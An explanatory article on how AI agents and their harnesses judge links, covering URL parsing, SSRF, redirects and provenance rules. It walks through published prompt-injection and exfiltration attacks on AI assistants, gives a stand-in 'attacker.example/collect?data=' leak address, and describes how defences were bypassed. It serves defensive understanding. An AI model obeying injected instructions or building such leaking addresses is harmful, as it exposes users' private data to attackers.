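# How AI agents decide which links and websites to trust

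## What an agent decides when it meets a link

An AI agent is a language model that can call tools, such as a web browser or a program that downloads pages, to carry out a task for a user. The software around the model, called the harness, runs those tool calls and can refuse them. Agents read mail, search the web, fill in forms and write research summaries, and much of that work involves links. For each link, the model or the harness must decide whether to open the address, what to send there, and whether to present the page to the user as reliable.

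Suppose an agent that handles a small company's bills receives an email with an invoice and a link for viewing and paying it. The agent opens the link, reads the page, enters the company's card details in its form, and sends the owner a link to the receipt. This errand involves three decisions with different risks. The agent *fetches* when it requests an address and reads what comes back. It *submits* when it sends something that belongs to the user, such as a password, personal details or a payment. It *cites* when it gives the user a page or link as a source or a next step.

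Criminals already target software that handles email. On October 22, 2026, the email security company Sublime Security observed a batch of fake invoices for about $88,000 each. *Prompt Injection Goes After the Inbox* (Trent, 2026) reports that the messages impersonated a cybersecurity company, posed as notes from the target's own chief executive or co-founder, and offered a 10% discount that was about to expire. Most went to financial controllers. To a person, they looked like ordinary invoice fraud, but they also contained hidden text meant for software that summarizes mail or acts on it.

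### The parts of an address

A web address, or URL, has several parts, and checking an agent's links requires telling them apart. Suppose the invoice link is `https://pay.example.com/invoices/4471?customer=ada#total`.

| Part | In the example | What it does |
|---|---|---|
| Scheme | `https` | Sets the protocol for the request |
| Host | `pay.example.com` | Names the server |
| Registrable domain | `example.com` | The part of the host that someone registers and controls |
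| Path | `/invoices/4471` | Points to a resource on that server |
| Query | `customer=ada` | Gives the server extra parameters |
| Fragment | `total` | Marks a spot within the page |

The registrable domain takes the most care to identify. WHATWG's *URL*, the standard for web addresses, defines it as the public suffix, an ending under which people can register names, plus the one label before it. web.dev, a guide for web developers, gives `com`, `com.au` and `github.io` as examples of public suffixes. So `pay.example.com` and `www.example.com` share an owner, while two sites that end in `github.io` usually do not.

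When the agent fetches the link, it sends nearly all of the URL to the server. The first line of the request contains the path and query, and another line contains the host. Only the fragment is not sent, according to MDN's *What is a URL?* The path and query can hold almost any text, so fetching a link can also pass information to whoever runs the server.

That message usually ends up in a log. *Never Send Sensitive Information in the URL, Even Over HTTPS* (Miessler, 2015) explains that HTTPS hides the address from outsiders in transit, but the receiving server often logs it. *9.3 Sensitive data does not get sent in the URL*, an entry in OWASP's security checklist for web applications, lists browser history and proxy logs as other places the address may be recorded. *The HTTP QUERY Method* (Reschke, 2026), an internet standard, notes that servers are more likely to log a request's address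 than its content.

### What can go wrong

Fetching a link can leak data. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) describes the basic attack, called URL-based data exfiltration. The attacker gets a model to request a URL on the attacker's server with private data in the query, such as an email address or a document title, and then reads the data from the server's log. The user may not notice, because the request can happen in the background, such as when the agent loads an image or previews a link. The fetched page may also contain instructions written for the agent.

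Fetching a link can even change something on the server. Web software mostly fetches with GET requests, which by convention only retrieve data. But Connected: Internet Encyclopedia's *9.1.1 Safe Methods*, which reproduces an early version of the web's protocol standard, says nobody can guarantee that a server will do nothing else in response. The programmer Simon Willison records an example in *45 posts tagged "exfiltration-attacks"*, his running collection of data thefts. A malicious email caused Superhuman AI, a mail assistant, to send the contents of dozens of other messages to an attacker's Google Form. Loading an image was enough to submit the data, because Google Forms stores data that arrives in a plain GET request.

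The loss from an ordinary submission is more direct, because a password gives an attacker access to the account and a payment may be hard to get back. The security company Zscaler found websites with hidden text meant to steer agents into making cryptocurrency payments, as Mascellino (2026) reported in *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents*. Researchers have also built scam sites to measure how often agents fall for them. A fraudster can also use a legitimate payment service to collect on a false invoice.

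A bad citation harms the reader, who may act on it long after the agent has finished. In *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities* (2026), the security firm Trail of Bits planted text in a PDF and in a note on the code-sharing site GitHub, and got a browser agent to state that Yuri Gagarin was the first man on the moon and to recommend a company that does not exist. Passing on an attack is more dangerous than passing on a false claim. In *How we helped Bunq secure their financial AI assistant*, Vissers and Van hamme (2026) sent a bank customer €0.02 with planted text in the transfer's description field. When the customer asked the bank's assistant about recent transactions, the assistant read the description and delivered a phishing message, which impersonates a trusted party to obtain credentials, data or money. The message appeared inside the bank's own app,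 where a customer has little reason to doubt it.

### Prompt injection and the lethal trifecta

Most of these cases depend on prompt injection, which is text in a page, message or file that the model treats as an instruction even though the user did not give it. Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, explains why models are open to it. The user's request, the developer's rules and the text of a web page all reach the model as one sequence of tokens (fragments of text), and nothing in that sequence reliably separates what the user wants from what a stranger wrote. Willison, who coined the term "prompt injection", distinguishes these attacks, in which the user is the victim, from jailbreaking, in which the user tries to make the model misbehave.

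How common prompt injection is outside the laboratory depends on the target. *Adversarial prompt injection payload for evading AI-based detection* (Scholten and Filar, June 2026) reported that almost all the prompt injection Sublime Security had been seeing in the wild tried to make AI security tools classify a malicious message as harmless. Few of the attacks targeted agents that act for a user. The Zscaler finding and the October invoices suggest that this is changing. So do the phishing emails that the security company Barracuda found, which target both the human reader and the AI assistant (Mascellino (2026), in *Attackers Hide AI Prompt Injections Inside Phishing Emails*).

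OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) gives one figure for how often an attack works. Outside researchers had reported an email, written as a dull follow-up about a restructuring, that contained instructions for the assistant to submit an employee's name and address to a supposed compliance system. In testing, it worked 50% of the time when the user asked ChatGPT to research the day's mail. This was one attack on one 2025 product, so the figure doesn't indicate an average success rate. But the email is typical of the better attacks, which use social engineering, a plausible story with no obviously malicious phrase in it. OpenAI finds that filters which classify incoming text usually miss such messages, because catching them means detecting a lie, often without the context that would expose it.

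Willison's "lethal trifecta" is the combination that lets a successful injection steal data: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to send data out. The invoice agent has all three. Its mailbox is private, anyone can write to it, and opening a link sends a web address to a stranger's server. A single tool can also combine all three. Willison's example is GitHub's connector for agents, which could read issues that an attacker had filed, read private code, and create pull requests (proposed code changes) that exposed it. In June 2025 he listed 17 such attacks, on products from OpenAI, Google, Microsoft, Amazon and others. The vendors had fixed almost all of them promptly, usually by blocking the outbound route. Removing any one of the three elements stops the theft, and the outbound route is generally the easiest to remove.

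The trifecta describes how data gets stolen, but two of the three decisions can go wrong even when the trifecta is absent. A fake invoice can work on an agent that reads untrusted mail and can make payments, even if the agent has no access to secrets. A false citation can mislead a user whenever the agent reads untrusted content and the user believes its answer. OpenAI uses a broader scheme that also covers these cases. In it, an attacker needs a source, which is a way to influence the system, and a sink, which is a capability that becomes dangerous in the wrong context. Following a link and making a payment are both sinks.

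### Where a check can sit

A developer can add a link check in four places. The places differ most in what happens when the model tries to follow an attacker's injected instructions.

| Place | Example of a check | Can a persuaded model override it? |
|---|---|---|
| Model | Training to refuse suspicious requests | Yes |
| Harness | A fetch tool that rejects addresses the model composed itself | No |
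| Browser or app | A policy on which sites the app may load images from | No |
| Network | A list of domains that traffic may reach | No |

OpenAI reports that most of the attacks it knows of against ChatGPT fail because the model refuses. But this defense relies on the same judgment the attacker is trying to manipulate. Willison calls blocking 99% of attacks a failing grade in application security, because an attacker can keep trying until one gets through. If each attempt has a 1% chance of success and the attempts are independent, an attacker who makes a hundred has a 63% chance of succeeding at least once. OpenAI draws a similar conclusion from customer service, where a company expects callers to mislead its staff now and then, so it also uses software to cap the refunds an employee can give.

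The other three places work like that cap. Anthropic's web fetch tool, the harness example in the table, will not request an address that the model has made up, regardless of the model's reasoning. Anthropic's Claude Cowork, an agent that works with a user's files, by default allows outgoing traffic only to listed domains.

A more general harness check inspects every tool call before it runs. *AgentTrust* (May 2026) describes one with 170 policy rules that adds only milliseconds when the rules alone can decide. The check sends ambiguous cases to a second language model, which acts as judge. The "No" in the table is therefore less certain, because an attacker who can influence what the judge reads may be able to manipulate it too.

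A "No" in the table also applies only to the routes that the check guards. In one test that Willison describes, planted instructions led the model in Google's coding tool Antigravity to look for a file of credentials. The file-reading tools blocked access to the file, so the model used the command line, where the restriction did not apply. A network check covers requests from every tool if all of the agent's traffic passes through it, but it usually has less information about each request. With HTTPS, it can ordinarily read the host but not the path or query, unless the operator decrypts the traffic. The harness has the full address and can also keep track of where that address came from.

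### The site and the request

People tend to judge a link by whether they trust the site. An agent also has to judge whether the particular request is safe to make, and the two answers can differ. In the Superhuman case, the site belonged to Google, but the request still sent private mail to an attacker. Many reputable sites also redirect visitors to other addresses, so a request can start at a trusted domain and end somewhere else.

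Opening a published article, even on an obscure blog, is unlikely to reveal anything private if its address was public before the conversation began. OpenAI relies on this when it lets ChatGPT automatically open only the exact addresses that an independent crawler has already seen. OpenAI adds that this rule does not make the page trustworthy. The article may still be wrong or contain a prompt injection. The paper *AgentTrust* (June 2026) takes the same approach to tool calls in general, applying trust to each action rather than to the agent as a whole.

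When an agent fetches a link, it mainly has to judge whether the request is safe to send, provided the harness treats whatever comes back as untrusted. When it cites a page, it has to judge the page and whether it supports the claim. Before submitting anything, it has to check both the request and the page, and sometimes more. If the bill-paying agent opens the invoice link exactly as it arrived, the address contains only what the sender put there, though the sender learns that someone opened the email. Even if the page loads safely and has a valid form on a well-known payment service, that isn't evidence that the company owes the money. To check that, the agent would have to look at the company's records, such as a purchase order or the account details already on file for the supplier.

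## Working out which site an address belongs to

Before the bill-paying agent can compare an invoice link with the supplier's details on file, something has to work out which site the link leads to. The harness is better placed to do this than the model. The job follows fixed rules, and both models and people can misread an address that someone has disguised. The steps, in order, are:

1. Parse the address with a standard URL parser, and refuse it if parsing fails.
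2. Normalise the host, so that different spellings of the same host become identical.
3. Find the registrable domain by looking up the host's ending in the Public Suffix List.
4. Compare the result with the expected domain by whole labels, the pieces of text between the dots.
5. Look up the host's numeric IP address, refuse private ones, and connect only to an address that passed.
6. If the server replies with a redirect, start again at step 1 with the new address.

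### Six links and their correct readings

Suppose the supplier is Acorn, an invented company whose site is `acorn.example`. Any of the links below could appear in an email about an Acorn invoice. Internet standards reserve `.example`, `example.net` and `example.org` for documentation, so none of the links leads to a real company.

| Link | Host | Registrable domain | Correct reading |
|---|---|---|---|
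| `https://pay.acorn.example/4471` | `pay.acorn.example` | `acorn.example` | Acorn's own site |
| `https://acorn.example.net/4471` | `acorn.example.net` | `example.net` | Another owner's site, with Acorn's name in the subdomain |
| `https://example.net/acorn.example/4471` | `example.net` | `example.net` | Another owner's site, with Acorn's name in the path |
| `https://acorn.example@example.net/4471` | `example.net` | `example.net` | Another owner's site, with Acorn's name as a username |
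| `https://аcorn.example/4471` | `xn--corn-43d.example` | `xn--corn-43d.example` | A different domain, whose first letter is a Cyrillic "а" |
| `https://example.org/a7Qx` | `example.org` | `example.org` | A link shortener, with the destination still unknown |

Control over a host runs from right to left in its address, the opposite of the order in which people read it. Whoever owns `example.net` can create any subdomain of it, including `acorn.example.net`, without Acorn's permission. The owner also chooses the site's paths, so a path is just as easy to fake.

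The text before an @ sign is a username, and sometimes a password, for logging in to the host that follows. WHATWG classes credentials in a web address as an error that does not stop the parser. A harness can be stricter and refuse such links, since ordinary web pages rarely need them.

The Cyrillic letter "а" looks the same as the Latin "a" in many fonts, so two different domain names can look identical. The domain name system (DNS), which translates hosts into IP addresses, traditionally works with a small set of Latin letters, digits and hyphens. Software therefore converts names with other characters into a code called Punycode, which begins with `xn--`. After conversion, the two names no longer look the same. Many honest sites have names in other alphabets, so Punycode alone isn't evidence of fraud. Lookalikes can also be made from ordinary Latin letters and digits. WHATWG's examples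 of confusable text include "m" and "rn", and the digit 0 and the letter O. An exact comparison rejects all of these lookalikes, but only if the harness knows which domain to expect.

### Parsing and normalising

A parser is the code that splits an address into its parts, and two parsers can split the same text differently. Claroty's *Exploiting URL Parsing Confusion*, a joint study with the security company Snyk, found major differences among many libraries and tools. These differences are dangerous when one library checks a link and another fetches it, because the first may find Acorn's host in the link while the second connects somewhere else. Daniel Stenberg, who created the download tool curl, warned in *Don't mix URL parsers* (2022) that using different parsers this way can produce security vulnerabilities.

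Parsers can read the same address differently, partly because there are two competing standards. According to *Parsing Millions of URLs per Second* (2023), WHATWG's standard requires parsers to ignore tab characters in an address, while a parser built on the older standard, such as curl's, would reject the address. The paper also found that the standard libraries of Java, Go, PHP and Python did not support WHATWG's version. Newer releases may differ, but developers don't have to track the changes if the harness parses each address once, rebuilds it from the parsed parts, and gives the fetching code the rebuilt version instead of the original text. This leaves much less room for a second parser to read the address differently.

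Rebuilding the address also normalises it. WHATWG's procedure lowercases the domain, decodes percent-encoded characters, and applies the Punycode conversion. It also converts IP addresses in unusual notation to the standard form, so the host `0` becomes `0.0.0.0` and `0xffffffff` becomes `255.255.255.255`. A filter that searches the original text for IP addresses written as four numbers separated by dots would miss both.

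Even after normalising, WHATWG treats `example.com` and `example.com.`, with a final dot, as different domains. A harness written for the first should either refuse the second or have an explicit rule for it.

### Finding the registrable domain

Under `.com`, people register the label just before the ending. Under `.uk`, many register the label before `co.uk`. A harness that kept only the last two labels would treat every company's site under `co.uk` as having the same owner. Each registry sets its own policy, so no formula works for all endings. The Public Suffix List, which Mozilla volunteers maintain with submissions from registries, lists the endings individually. Browsers use it to stop one site from setting cookies for every other site under `co.uk`.

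The Public Suffix List usually changes a few times a week, according to its download page, so the harness's copy needs regular updates. With an old copy, the harness could treat the customers of a newly listed hosting service as a single owner.

WHATWG warns that the registrable domain cannot provide a hard security boundary, because programs use different versions of the list. It recommends comparing origins instead. An origin combines the scheme, the host and the port (a number that identifies a service on the server). The registrable domain is enough to expose the disguised links in the table, but a harness should compare the whole origin before sending a password, since different people may run different subdomains of the same domain.

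### Why prefix and substring matching fail

Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, had a comparison error of this kind. Its WebFetch tool could fetch pages from certain trusted domains without asking the user. Before version 1.0.111, the tool checked only whether a domain started with the name of a trusted one, such as `docs.python.org` or `modelcontextprotocol.io`. NVD's *CVE-2026-24052 Detail*, an entry in the US government's vulnerability database, gives the example of `modelcontextprotocol.io.example.com`, which would have passed even though it belongs to the owner of `example.com`.

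The flaw could have let an attacker trigger automatic requests to a server they controlled and possibly steal data. Its severity score was 7.1 out of 10, which is rated high. The advisory came out on February 3, 2026. OSV's *GHSA-vhw5-3g5m-8ggf* (2026), which reproduces the advisory's text, adds that users with automatic updates had already received the fix. Neither entry mentions an actual attack.

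The link `https://acorn.example.net/4471` would wrongly pass the same test, because its host starts with `acorn.example`. Searching for `acorn.example` anywhere in the link is worse, since that also accepts the links with Acorn's name in the path and before the @ sign. Testing only the end of the host fails too, because anyone could register `notacorn.example`, which ends with `acorn.example`.

A correct test accepts a host if it equals `acorn.example` or ends with `.acorn.example`. The leading dot ensures that the match begins at the start of a label. Path rules need the same care, because a path that begins with `foobar` also begins with `foo`. WHATWG recommends comparing whole path segments, and preferably not basing security decisions on paths at all.

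### Refusing private addresses

A host that passes these tests can still lead to a dangerous address, because whoever controls a domain decides which IP address it points to. That address may be private, meaning it leads to a machine on the same internal network or back to the machine making the request. An outsider normally can't reach private addresses, but an agent running inside the network can.

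Security engineers call the resulting attack server-side request forgery, or SSRF. MDN's *Server Side Request Forgery (SSRF)* gives the example of an app that downloads an image from any address a user supplies. If the app never checks the address, the user can supply one on the company's intranet and receive an internal page. Attackers often use SSRF to get a level deeper into a network, according to Include Security's *Mitigating SSRF in 2023* (2023). Most cloud providers offer a metadata service at a fixed internal address. OWASP's *A10:2021* (2021) warns that an attacker who gets a server to query that service can obtain sensitive information.

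In *AgentLens*, Lv, Chen and colleagues (2026) found this flaw in Aider, a popular open-source coding agent. They prepared a software project whose README file (its introductory notes) presented a cloud metadata address as a source of internal documentation, then told Aider to fetch that address. Aider asks the user to confirm before it fetches a link, but neither the confirmation step nor the downloading code checked whether the address was internal, so the request went out. The flaw is recorded as CVE-2026-10177.

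The test shows that Aider's software had no check to stop the request once the user had approved it. A person who sees only a numeric address in a confirmation box may not know where it leads. Because the researchers gave the instruction themselves, the test doesn't measure how often a README alone would persuade the model.

Agents that control a browser can expose sites where the user is already logged in, as well as internal pages. An individual draft posted with the IETF, which develops internet standards, describes public reports of server-side request forgery (SSRF) in a tool that lets agents operate a browser. The reported impact includes access to those logged-in sites because such tools may run with the user's own browser profile.

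OWASP recommends allowing only listed destinations and advises against relying on blocklists or text patterns, which attackers know how to get around. An agent that browses the open web can't list every site in advance, but its harness can still refuse whole ranges of private IP addresses if it checks the numeric address returned by the lookup rather than the text of the link. A firewall that blocks traffic to the internal network is a useful second barrier because it acts on the actual destination.

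The harness must also connect to the same IP address that it checked. If it looks up a host, approves the result, and then passes the hostname to a download library that looks it up again, an attacker who controls the domain's DNS records can return a public address the first time and a private one the second. This technique is known as DNS rebinding.

To prevent this, the harness should look up the host once, check every IP address returned, and connect to one that passed. It should still verify the site's HTTPS certificate against the host's name. If the agent's traffic goes through a proxy that does its own lookups, the proxy has to check the addresses.

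### Following redirects one step at a time

Many download libraries follow redirects automatically, so the harness may approve the first address without checking the destination. Link shorteners work by redirecting anyone who opens the short address to the stored long one. In one of MDN's examples of an attack, the attacker's public site passes the first check and then redirects the request to an internal address.

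OWASP advises disabling redirects. That suits a tool that calls a few fixed addresses, but for a browsing agent it would break every shortened link and many ordinary links that forward visitors from `http` to `https`. MDN recommends a more practical approach for browsing agents, in which the harness turns off automatic redirects, reads each new address from the server's reply, and runs the full set of checks on it before making another request. The harness also limits the number of redirects in a chain. A script on a page can send a browser to a new address without a server redirect, so a browser agent needs the same checks every time the page changes.

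Redirects also weaken checks based on a site's reputation, as OpenAI points out. Open redirects, pages that forward visitors to whatever address the link contains, are the easiest to exploit. *Claudy Day* (Luz, 2026), a report from the security company Oasis Security, describes one on Anthropic's claude.com. Any link that began with `claude.com/redirect/` sent the visitor to the address that followed, even if that address belonged to someone else.

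Google Ads validated links by their host, so an attacker could have placed a search ad that displayed a genuine claude.com address but sent anyone who clicked it to a different page. In Oasis's demonstration, that page was a new Claude chat containing hidden instructions.

Oasis reported the findings to Anthropic before publishing them on March 18, 2026. Anthropic had fixed the prompt injection, but according to Oasis's page, last updated on May 27, the remaining issues, including the redirect, were still being addressed.

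An agent that trusted claude.com and checked only the first address would have had the same weakness as Google Ads. Checking every address in the chain would expose a redirect to a stranger's site. But it might not have stopped the chain that Oasis built, which ended on claude.ai, another Anthropic domain. A harness that trusted both domains would have approved both steps.

### Malicious owners and shared sites

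An agent can read the domain correctly and still not know whether its owner is honest. A fraudster can register a domain, get a valid HTTPS certificate for it, and send out links that openly show it. In the invoice case, the harness can compare the domain with the one on file for Acorn, but when the agent has found a page through a search, there may be nothing to compare it with.

An honest company's domain may also host a stranger's page. The Public Suffix List separates the users of `github.io`, but it can't do so on a site that puts users' names in the path, where the domain identifies the company that runs the server but not the person who wrote the page. GitLab's *CVE-2026-54316* (2026) records that Claude Code once pre-approved all of huggingface.co, a site for sharing AI models, including any repository an attacker put there.

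## Keeping private data out of requested addresses

By reading an address correctly, the harness can identify which site will receive the request, but not whether the address contains private data, such as a line from the user's mail that an attacker has tricked the model into adding. Researchers have reported leaks of this kind since 2023. OpenAI and Anthropic each use ordinary software to enforce a rule against them. Because private text inside an address is hard to recognize, both rules depend mainly on where the address came from.

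### How the leak works

OpenAI illustrates the attack with the address `https://attacker.example/collect?data=<something private>`. The part in angle brackets is a blank for the model to fill in. Against the bill-paying agent, the attack would go like this:

1. The attacker sends the company an email that looks like a question about an invoice but contains instructions for the agent.
2. The owner asks the agent to go through the day's mail, and the agent reads the attacker's email along with the rest.
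3. The model follows the instructions. It picks out something private, such as the name of a customer who is behind on payments, and writes it into the blank.
4. The harness requests the finished address.
5. The attacker's server logs the address, and the attacker reads the customer's name in the log.

The server receives the name in the requested address even if it replies with an error or an empty page. Claude's fetch tool can send only GET requests, but this restriction doesn't prevent the leak, as dyb argues in *The Read-Only Lie*.

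The last chance to stop the leak comes just before step 4, when a harness could search the finished address for private text. But the model can encode the text so that it no longer resembles the original, or split it across several requests so that no single address looks suspicious.

### Requests that need no click

Three common features can send the request without any action by the user.

The best known is the display of images. Many chat apps show a model's answer as formatted text, and an image in that text is an address that the user's browser loads. If the model has put private data in the address, the browser sends the data out as soon as the answer appears. Willison calls this Markdown exfiltration, after the notation that models use to format their answers.

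Link previews can also leak private data. When someone posts a link in a messaging app, the app often fetches the page to show its title or picture. Willison (2024) describes the risk in the workplace app Slack, where an attacker could trick a chatbot with access to private data into posting a link that leaks the data when Slack previews it. An app that posts to Slack can turn off previews for its own messages, a precaution Willison credits to the security researcher Johann Rehberger. The security company PromptArmor warns of the same problem for people who talk to agents through messaging apps, and found that OpenClaw, one such agent, was exposed by default on Telegram. Without previews, the user would typically have to click the link for the data to leak.

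The agent's own fetch tool can also make the request in the background, often from the vendor's servers. *ShadowLeak*, a report by the security company Radware on one such attack, points out that the victim's employer can't see this traffic because it never passes through the employer's network or the victim's browser.

| Feature | What sends the request | Where a developer can stop it |
|---|---|---|
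| Image in an answer | The user's browser or app | The app's policy on which hosts may supply images |
| Link preview | The messaging service | The setting that turns previews off |
| Background fetch | The agent's fetch tool | A rule in the harness |

A control in one row has no effect on the other two, so a product with all three features needs all three controls.

### Published cases from 2023 to 2026

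Rehberger reported the image leak to OpenAI in early 2023. OpenAI had no bug bounty program then and showed little interest in fixing the problem, according to *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, a post on Rehberger's blog, Embrace The Red. Microsoft fixed the same flaw in Bing Chat in May 2023 with a content security policy, a header in which a website lists the hosts that a browser may load content from.

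In December 2023, OpenAI added its first defense, a check named `url_safe`. It was unclear how the check decided which addresses were safe, but Rehberger worked out parts of it from the outside. Rehberger presented ways around it at Black Hat Europe in 2024, and also found that some products, including ChatGPT's macOS and iOS apps, didn't have the check.

A content security policy has a different weakness. It controls which host the browser contacts, but that host may pass the request on. *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data*, from trackr.live, describes a permitted server fetching on the browser's behalf in an account of image leaks that covers EchoLeak and SearchLeak. Aim Security found EchoLeak, recorded as CVE-2025-32711, in Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant for office work. Willison's collection of data thefts also includes a May 2026 case in Microsoft's Copilot Cowork.

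The security company Varonis published SearchLeak on June 15, 2026. In Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026), the victim clicks a link to a genuine Microsoft address, and Copilot's enterprise search then sends data from the victim's mailbox to the attacker. The attack needed three flaws:

- Copilot treated the search text in the link as instructions.
- Copilot disarmed images in its answers only after it had finished writing, but the browser loaded each image while the answer was still arriving.
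- The content security policy allowed images from Bing, and Bing's image search would fetch any address that a request gave it.

The browser therefore contacted only Bing, as the policy required, and Bing's servers delivered the stolen text to the attacker. Varonis says the attack could reach anything the user could open through Copilot, including meeting notes, shared files and login codes sent by email. Microsoft rated the flaw (CVE-2026-42824) critical and has fixed it. Varonis demonstrated the attack and doesn't mention criminals using it.

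Varonis recommends cleaning an answer before the browser displays any of it. It also advises companies to check their lists of permitted hosts for services that fetch addresses on request, since any such service can carry data out.

### Anthropic's provenance rule

A provenance rule lets an agent fetch only addresses that came from an approved source. Anthropic's web fetch tool has had one since its release in September 2025. According to the developer documentation, *Web fetch tool*, the rule is meant to stop Claude from constructing its own addresses.

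In the example above, the attacker's email might contain the address up to `data=`. When the model adds the customer's name, it creates a new address that appears nowhere in the approved parts of the conversation, so the tool returns an error.

A newer Chinese edition of the documentation, Anthropic's *網頁擷取工具*, explains more fully what counts as an approved source. It refers to the system prompt, which contains the developer's standing instructions to the model, and to MCP connectors, which link the model to outside services through a common protocol.

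| Where the address has appeared | Does the tool accept it by default? |
|---|---|
| A message from the user | Yes |
| A result from a tool that the developer's own software runs | Yes |
| A result from an earlier web search or web fetch | Yes |
| Only in Claude's own output | No |
| Only in the system prompt | No |
| Only in results from Anthropic's code execution tool or an MCP connector | No |

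The second row leaves a gap, because a tool result can include an address that Claude composed. For example, if a developer gives Claude a tool that runs code, Claude can write code that prints an address. The fetch tool would then accept that address because it appeared in a tool result. An error message that quotes Claude's text can have the same effect. Developers can close this gap with Anthropic's `url_sources` setting, which can exclude one tool, several tools or a whole category of sources.

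When the tool came out, Willison (2025) wondered whether a harness could accept only addresses from the user's prompts, and was disappointed that Anthropic's rule was looser. Even the stricter rule would not be fully secure, because people paste other people's text into their messages. *Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection* (2024) suggests that a chatbot could refuse to open links whenever the prompt contains pasted text, but only as a temporary measure.

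Anthropic has also added a check on content. The tool rejects an address that appears to contain a password or an API key (a code that gives software access to a service), unless that credential also appears in the system prompt or the text of a user's message. This helps protect secrets with a recognizable form, but a customer's name or a sentence from a contract has none, so protecting that kind of data depends mostly on the provenance rule.

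Anthropic warns that some risk remains and advises developers to use the tool only in trusted environments or with data that isn't sensitive. Developers worried about leaks can also turn the tool off, restrict it to listed domains or limit the number of fetches.

### The Memory Heist

On July 9, 2026, Ayush Paul published *The Memory Heist*, an attack that got private data out of Claude without breaking the provenance rule. It targeted the ordinary Claude chat app, which can remember details from a user's past conversations and fetch web pages. Willison (2026) explains the attack in *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets*.

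The rule at the time let Claude open links on pages it had already fetched. Paul built a website for an invented coffee shop, with a set of links and a plausible reason for Claude to spell out the user's name by following them. Claude never wrote an address itself and opened only links from approved sources, but Paul could see on his server which links it chose, and those choices spelled out the user's name, home city and employer. The site showed the trap only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, so a person was less likely to notice it.

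Anthropic responded by stopping the fetch tool from opening links found on pages the tool had fetched. It didn't pay Paul a bounty, saying it had already found the problem internally. The fix makes browsing less convenient. For example, after fetching a supplier's home page, Claude can't open the payment terms linked there unless the address also comes from another approved source, such as a web search or the user.

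According to the newer documentation, the API version of Anthropic's tool (the one outside software uses) still accepts links from fetched pages by default, unlike the repaired chat app. A developer whose agent handles private data can change the `url_sources` setting to exclude web fetch results, which would make the agent behave much like the chat app.

### ShadowLeak and ZombieAgent

OpenAI had already been through a similar sequence. In ShadowLeak, Radware attacked Deep Research, a ChatGPT mode that spends several minutes reading sources before writing a report. With the user's permission, it could read Gmail as well as the web. When the user asked for research on the day's mail, one email from Radware was enough to make it send an employee's name and address to Radware's server.

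OpenAI's `url_safe` check limited where images could come from, but Radware observed no comparable limit on the addresses that the agent opened directly. The model rejected the early, blunt versions of the email and would not put raw personal details in an address. It complied when the email told it to encode the details first, supposedly for security. The fetch tool then received only a seemingly meaningless string, so scanning addresses for private text is not a reliable defense.

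Radware reports that the final version worked every time in repeated tests, but doesn't say how many it ran. The email closely resembles the restructuring message for which OpenAI later reported a 50% success rate, so the result may depend on the exact wording and on what the user asks. Radware reported the flaw on June 18, 2025, and OpenAI fixed it in early August.

After that, ChatGPT would open addresses only exactly as it had received them. Radware's *ZombieAgent* got around this rule as well, without ChatGPT breaking it. The attacker supplied a set of ready-made links in an email, and ChatGPT's choice among them revealed the data, much as in Paul's later attack on Claude.

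Radware also found ways to make the leak last and spread. It could plant instructions in ChatGPT's memory through a shared file, making the agent leak data in later conversations too. It could also collect email addresses from the victim's inbox, and the attacker's server would then send the same email to them. OpenAI had tried to prevent attacks through memory by blocking the use of memory in a chat that had already used a connected service such as Gmail, but it hadn't stopped ChatGPT from reading its memory first and the mailbox second.

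Radware reported ZombieAgent on September 26, 2025, and OpenAI fixed it on December 16. *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack* reports that ChatGPT would now open a link from an email only under limited conditions, such as when the link appears in a well-known public index.

### OpenAI's public-URL rule

Six weeks after the fix, on January 28, 2026, Adrian Spânu and Thomas Shadwell of OpenAI described a general rule built on the same idea. OpenAI runs a crawler, a program that records public web pages as a search engine does. The crawler has no access to users' conversations, accounts or personal data. When ChatGPT wants to load an address automatically, OpenAI's software applies the following procedure:

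1. It compares the exact address with those that the crawler has recorded.
2. If there is a match, ChatGPT loads the page or image.
3. If there is no match, the software either tells the agent to try a different website or shows the user a warning and waits for a decision.

In the invoice example, the crawler might have recorded the attacker's address up to `data=`, but it would be unlikely to have recorded the version with the customer's name at the end. The comparison has to cover the whole address, because a match on the domain alone would accept both versions.

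The warning tells the user that OpenAI could not verify the link and that the address may include information from the conversation. It displays the address so the user can look for anything that should not be there, though most people would find an encoded secret hard to spot.

OpenAI considered using a list of well-known sites instead. It concluded that, besides the problem with redirects, such a list would raise too many false alarms because people visit many sites beyond the most popular ones. Rehberger writes on Embrace The Red that ChatGPT also appears to treat an address the user typed in a chat as safe for the rest of that chat.

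The public-URL rule would probably have stopped the Memory Heist, because Paul's server generated new links as Claude went along and an independent crawler would not have recorded them all in advance. But an attacker can publish a fixed set of pages, wait for the crawler to record them, and then infer private data from which ones the agent opens. Rehberger notes that anyone with a fairly large blog probably already has 36 recorded pages, enough for one per letter and digit. OpenAI's accompanying paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*, acknowledges this leak, according to Rehberger, who still considers the rule a significant improvement.

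### How much a choice of links can reveal

Both rules greatly reduce how much an attacker can learn from each request. Anthropic's tool accepts addresses of up to 250 characters. If the model could fill 200 of those with data, choosing each from 64 symbols, one request would carry 1,200 bits. (A bit is the information in the answer to a yes-or-no question when both answers are equally likely.) A choice among 36 existing links carries only about 5 bits.

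The total depends on two numbers. Let N be the number of permitted links that the attacker can tell apart in a server log, and k the number of fetches that the agent makes. Each fetch is a choice among N links, so there are N<sup>k</sup> possible sequences. The most that the sequence can reveal is therefore:

bits = log<sub>2</sub>(N<sup>k</sup>) = k × log<sub>2</sub>(N)

With 36 links, log<sub>2</sub>(36) is about 5.17. Five fetches can reveal about 26 bits, enough to pick out one of 60 million possibilities.

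| Permitted links (N) | Fetches (k) | Maximum leak |
|---|---|---|
| 36 | 1 | 5 bits |
| 36 | 5 | 26 bits |
| 36 | 10 | 52 bits |
| 1,000 | 5 | 50 bits |
| 1,000 | 10 | 100 bits |

*Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection* describes an attack that revealed one character of private data with each address ChatGPT opened. In 2024, ChatGPT opened at most 10 addresses per prompt, so the attack could reveal at most 10 characters per prompt. Opening several addresses also took longer than opening one, which gave the user more time to notice the attack and stop it.

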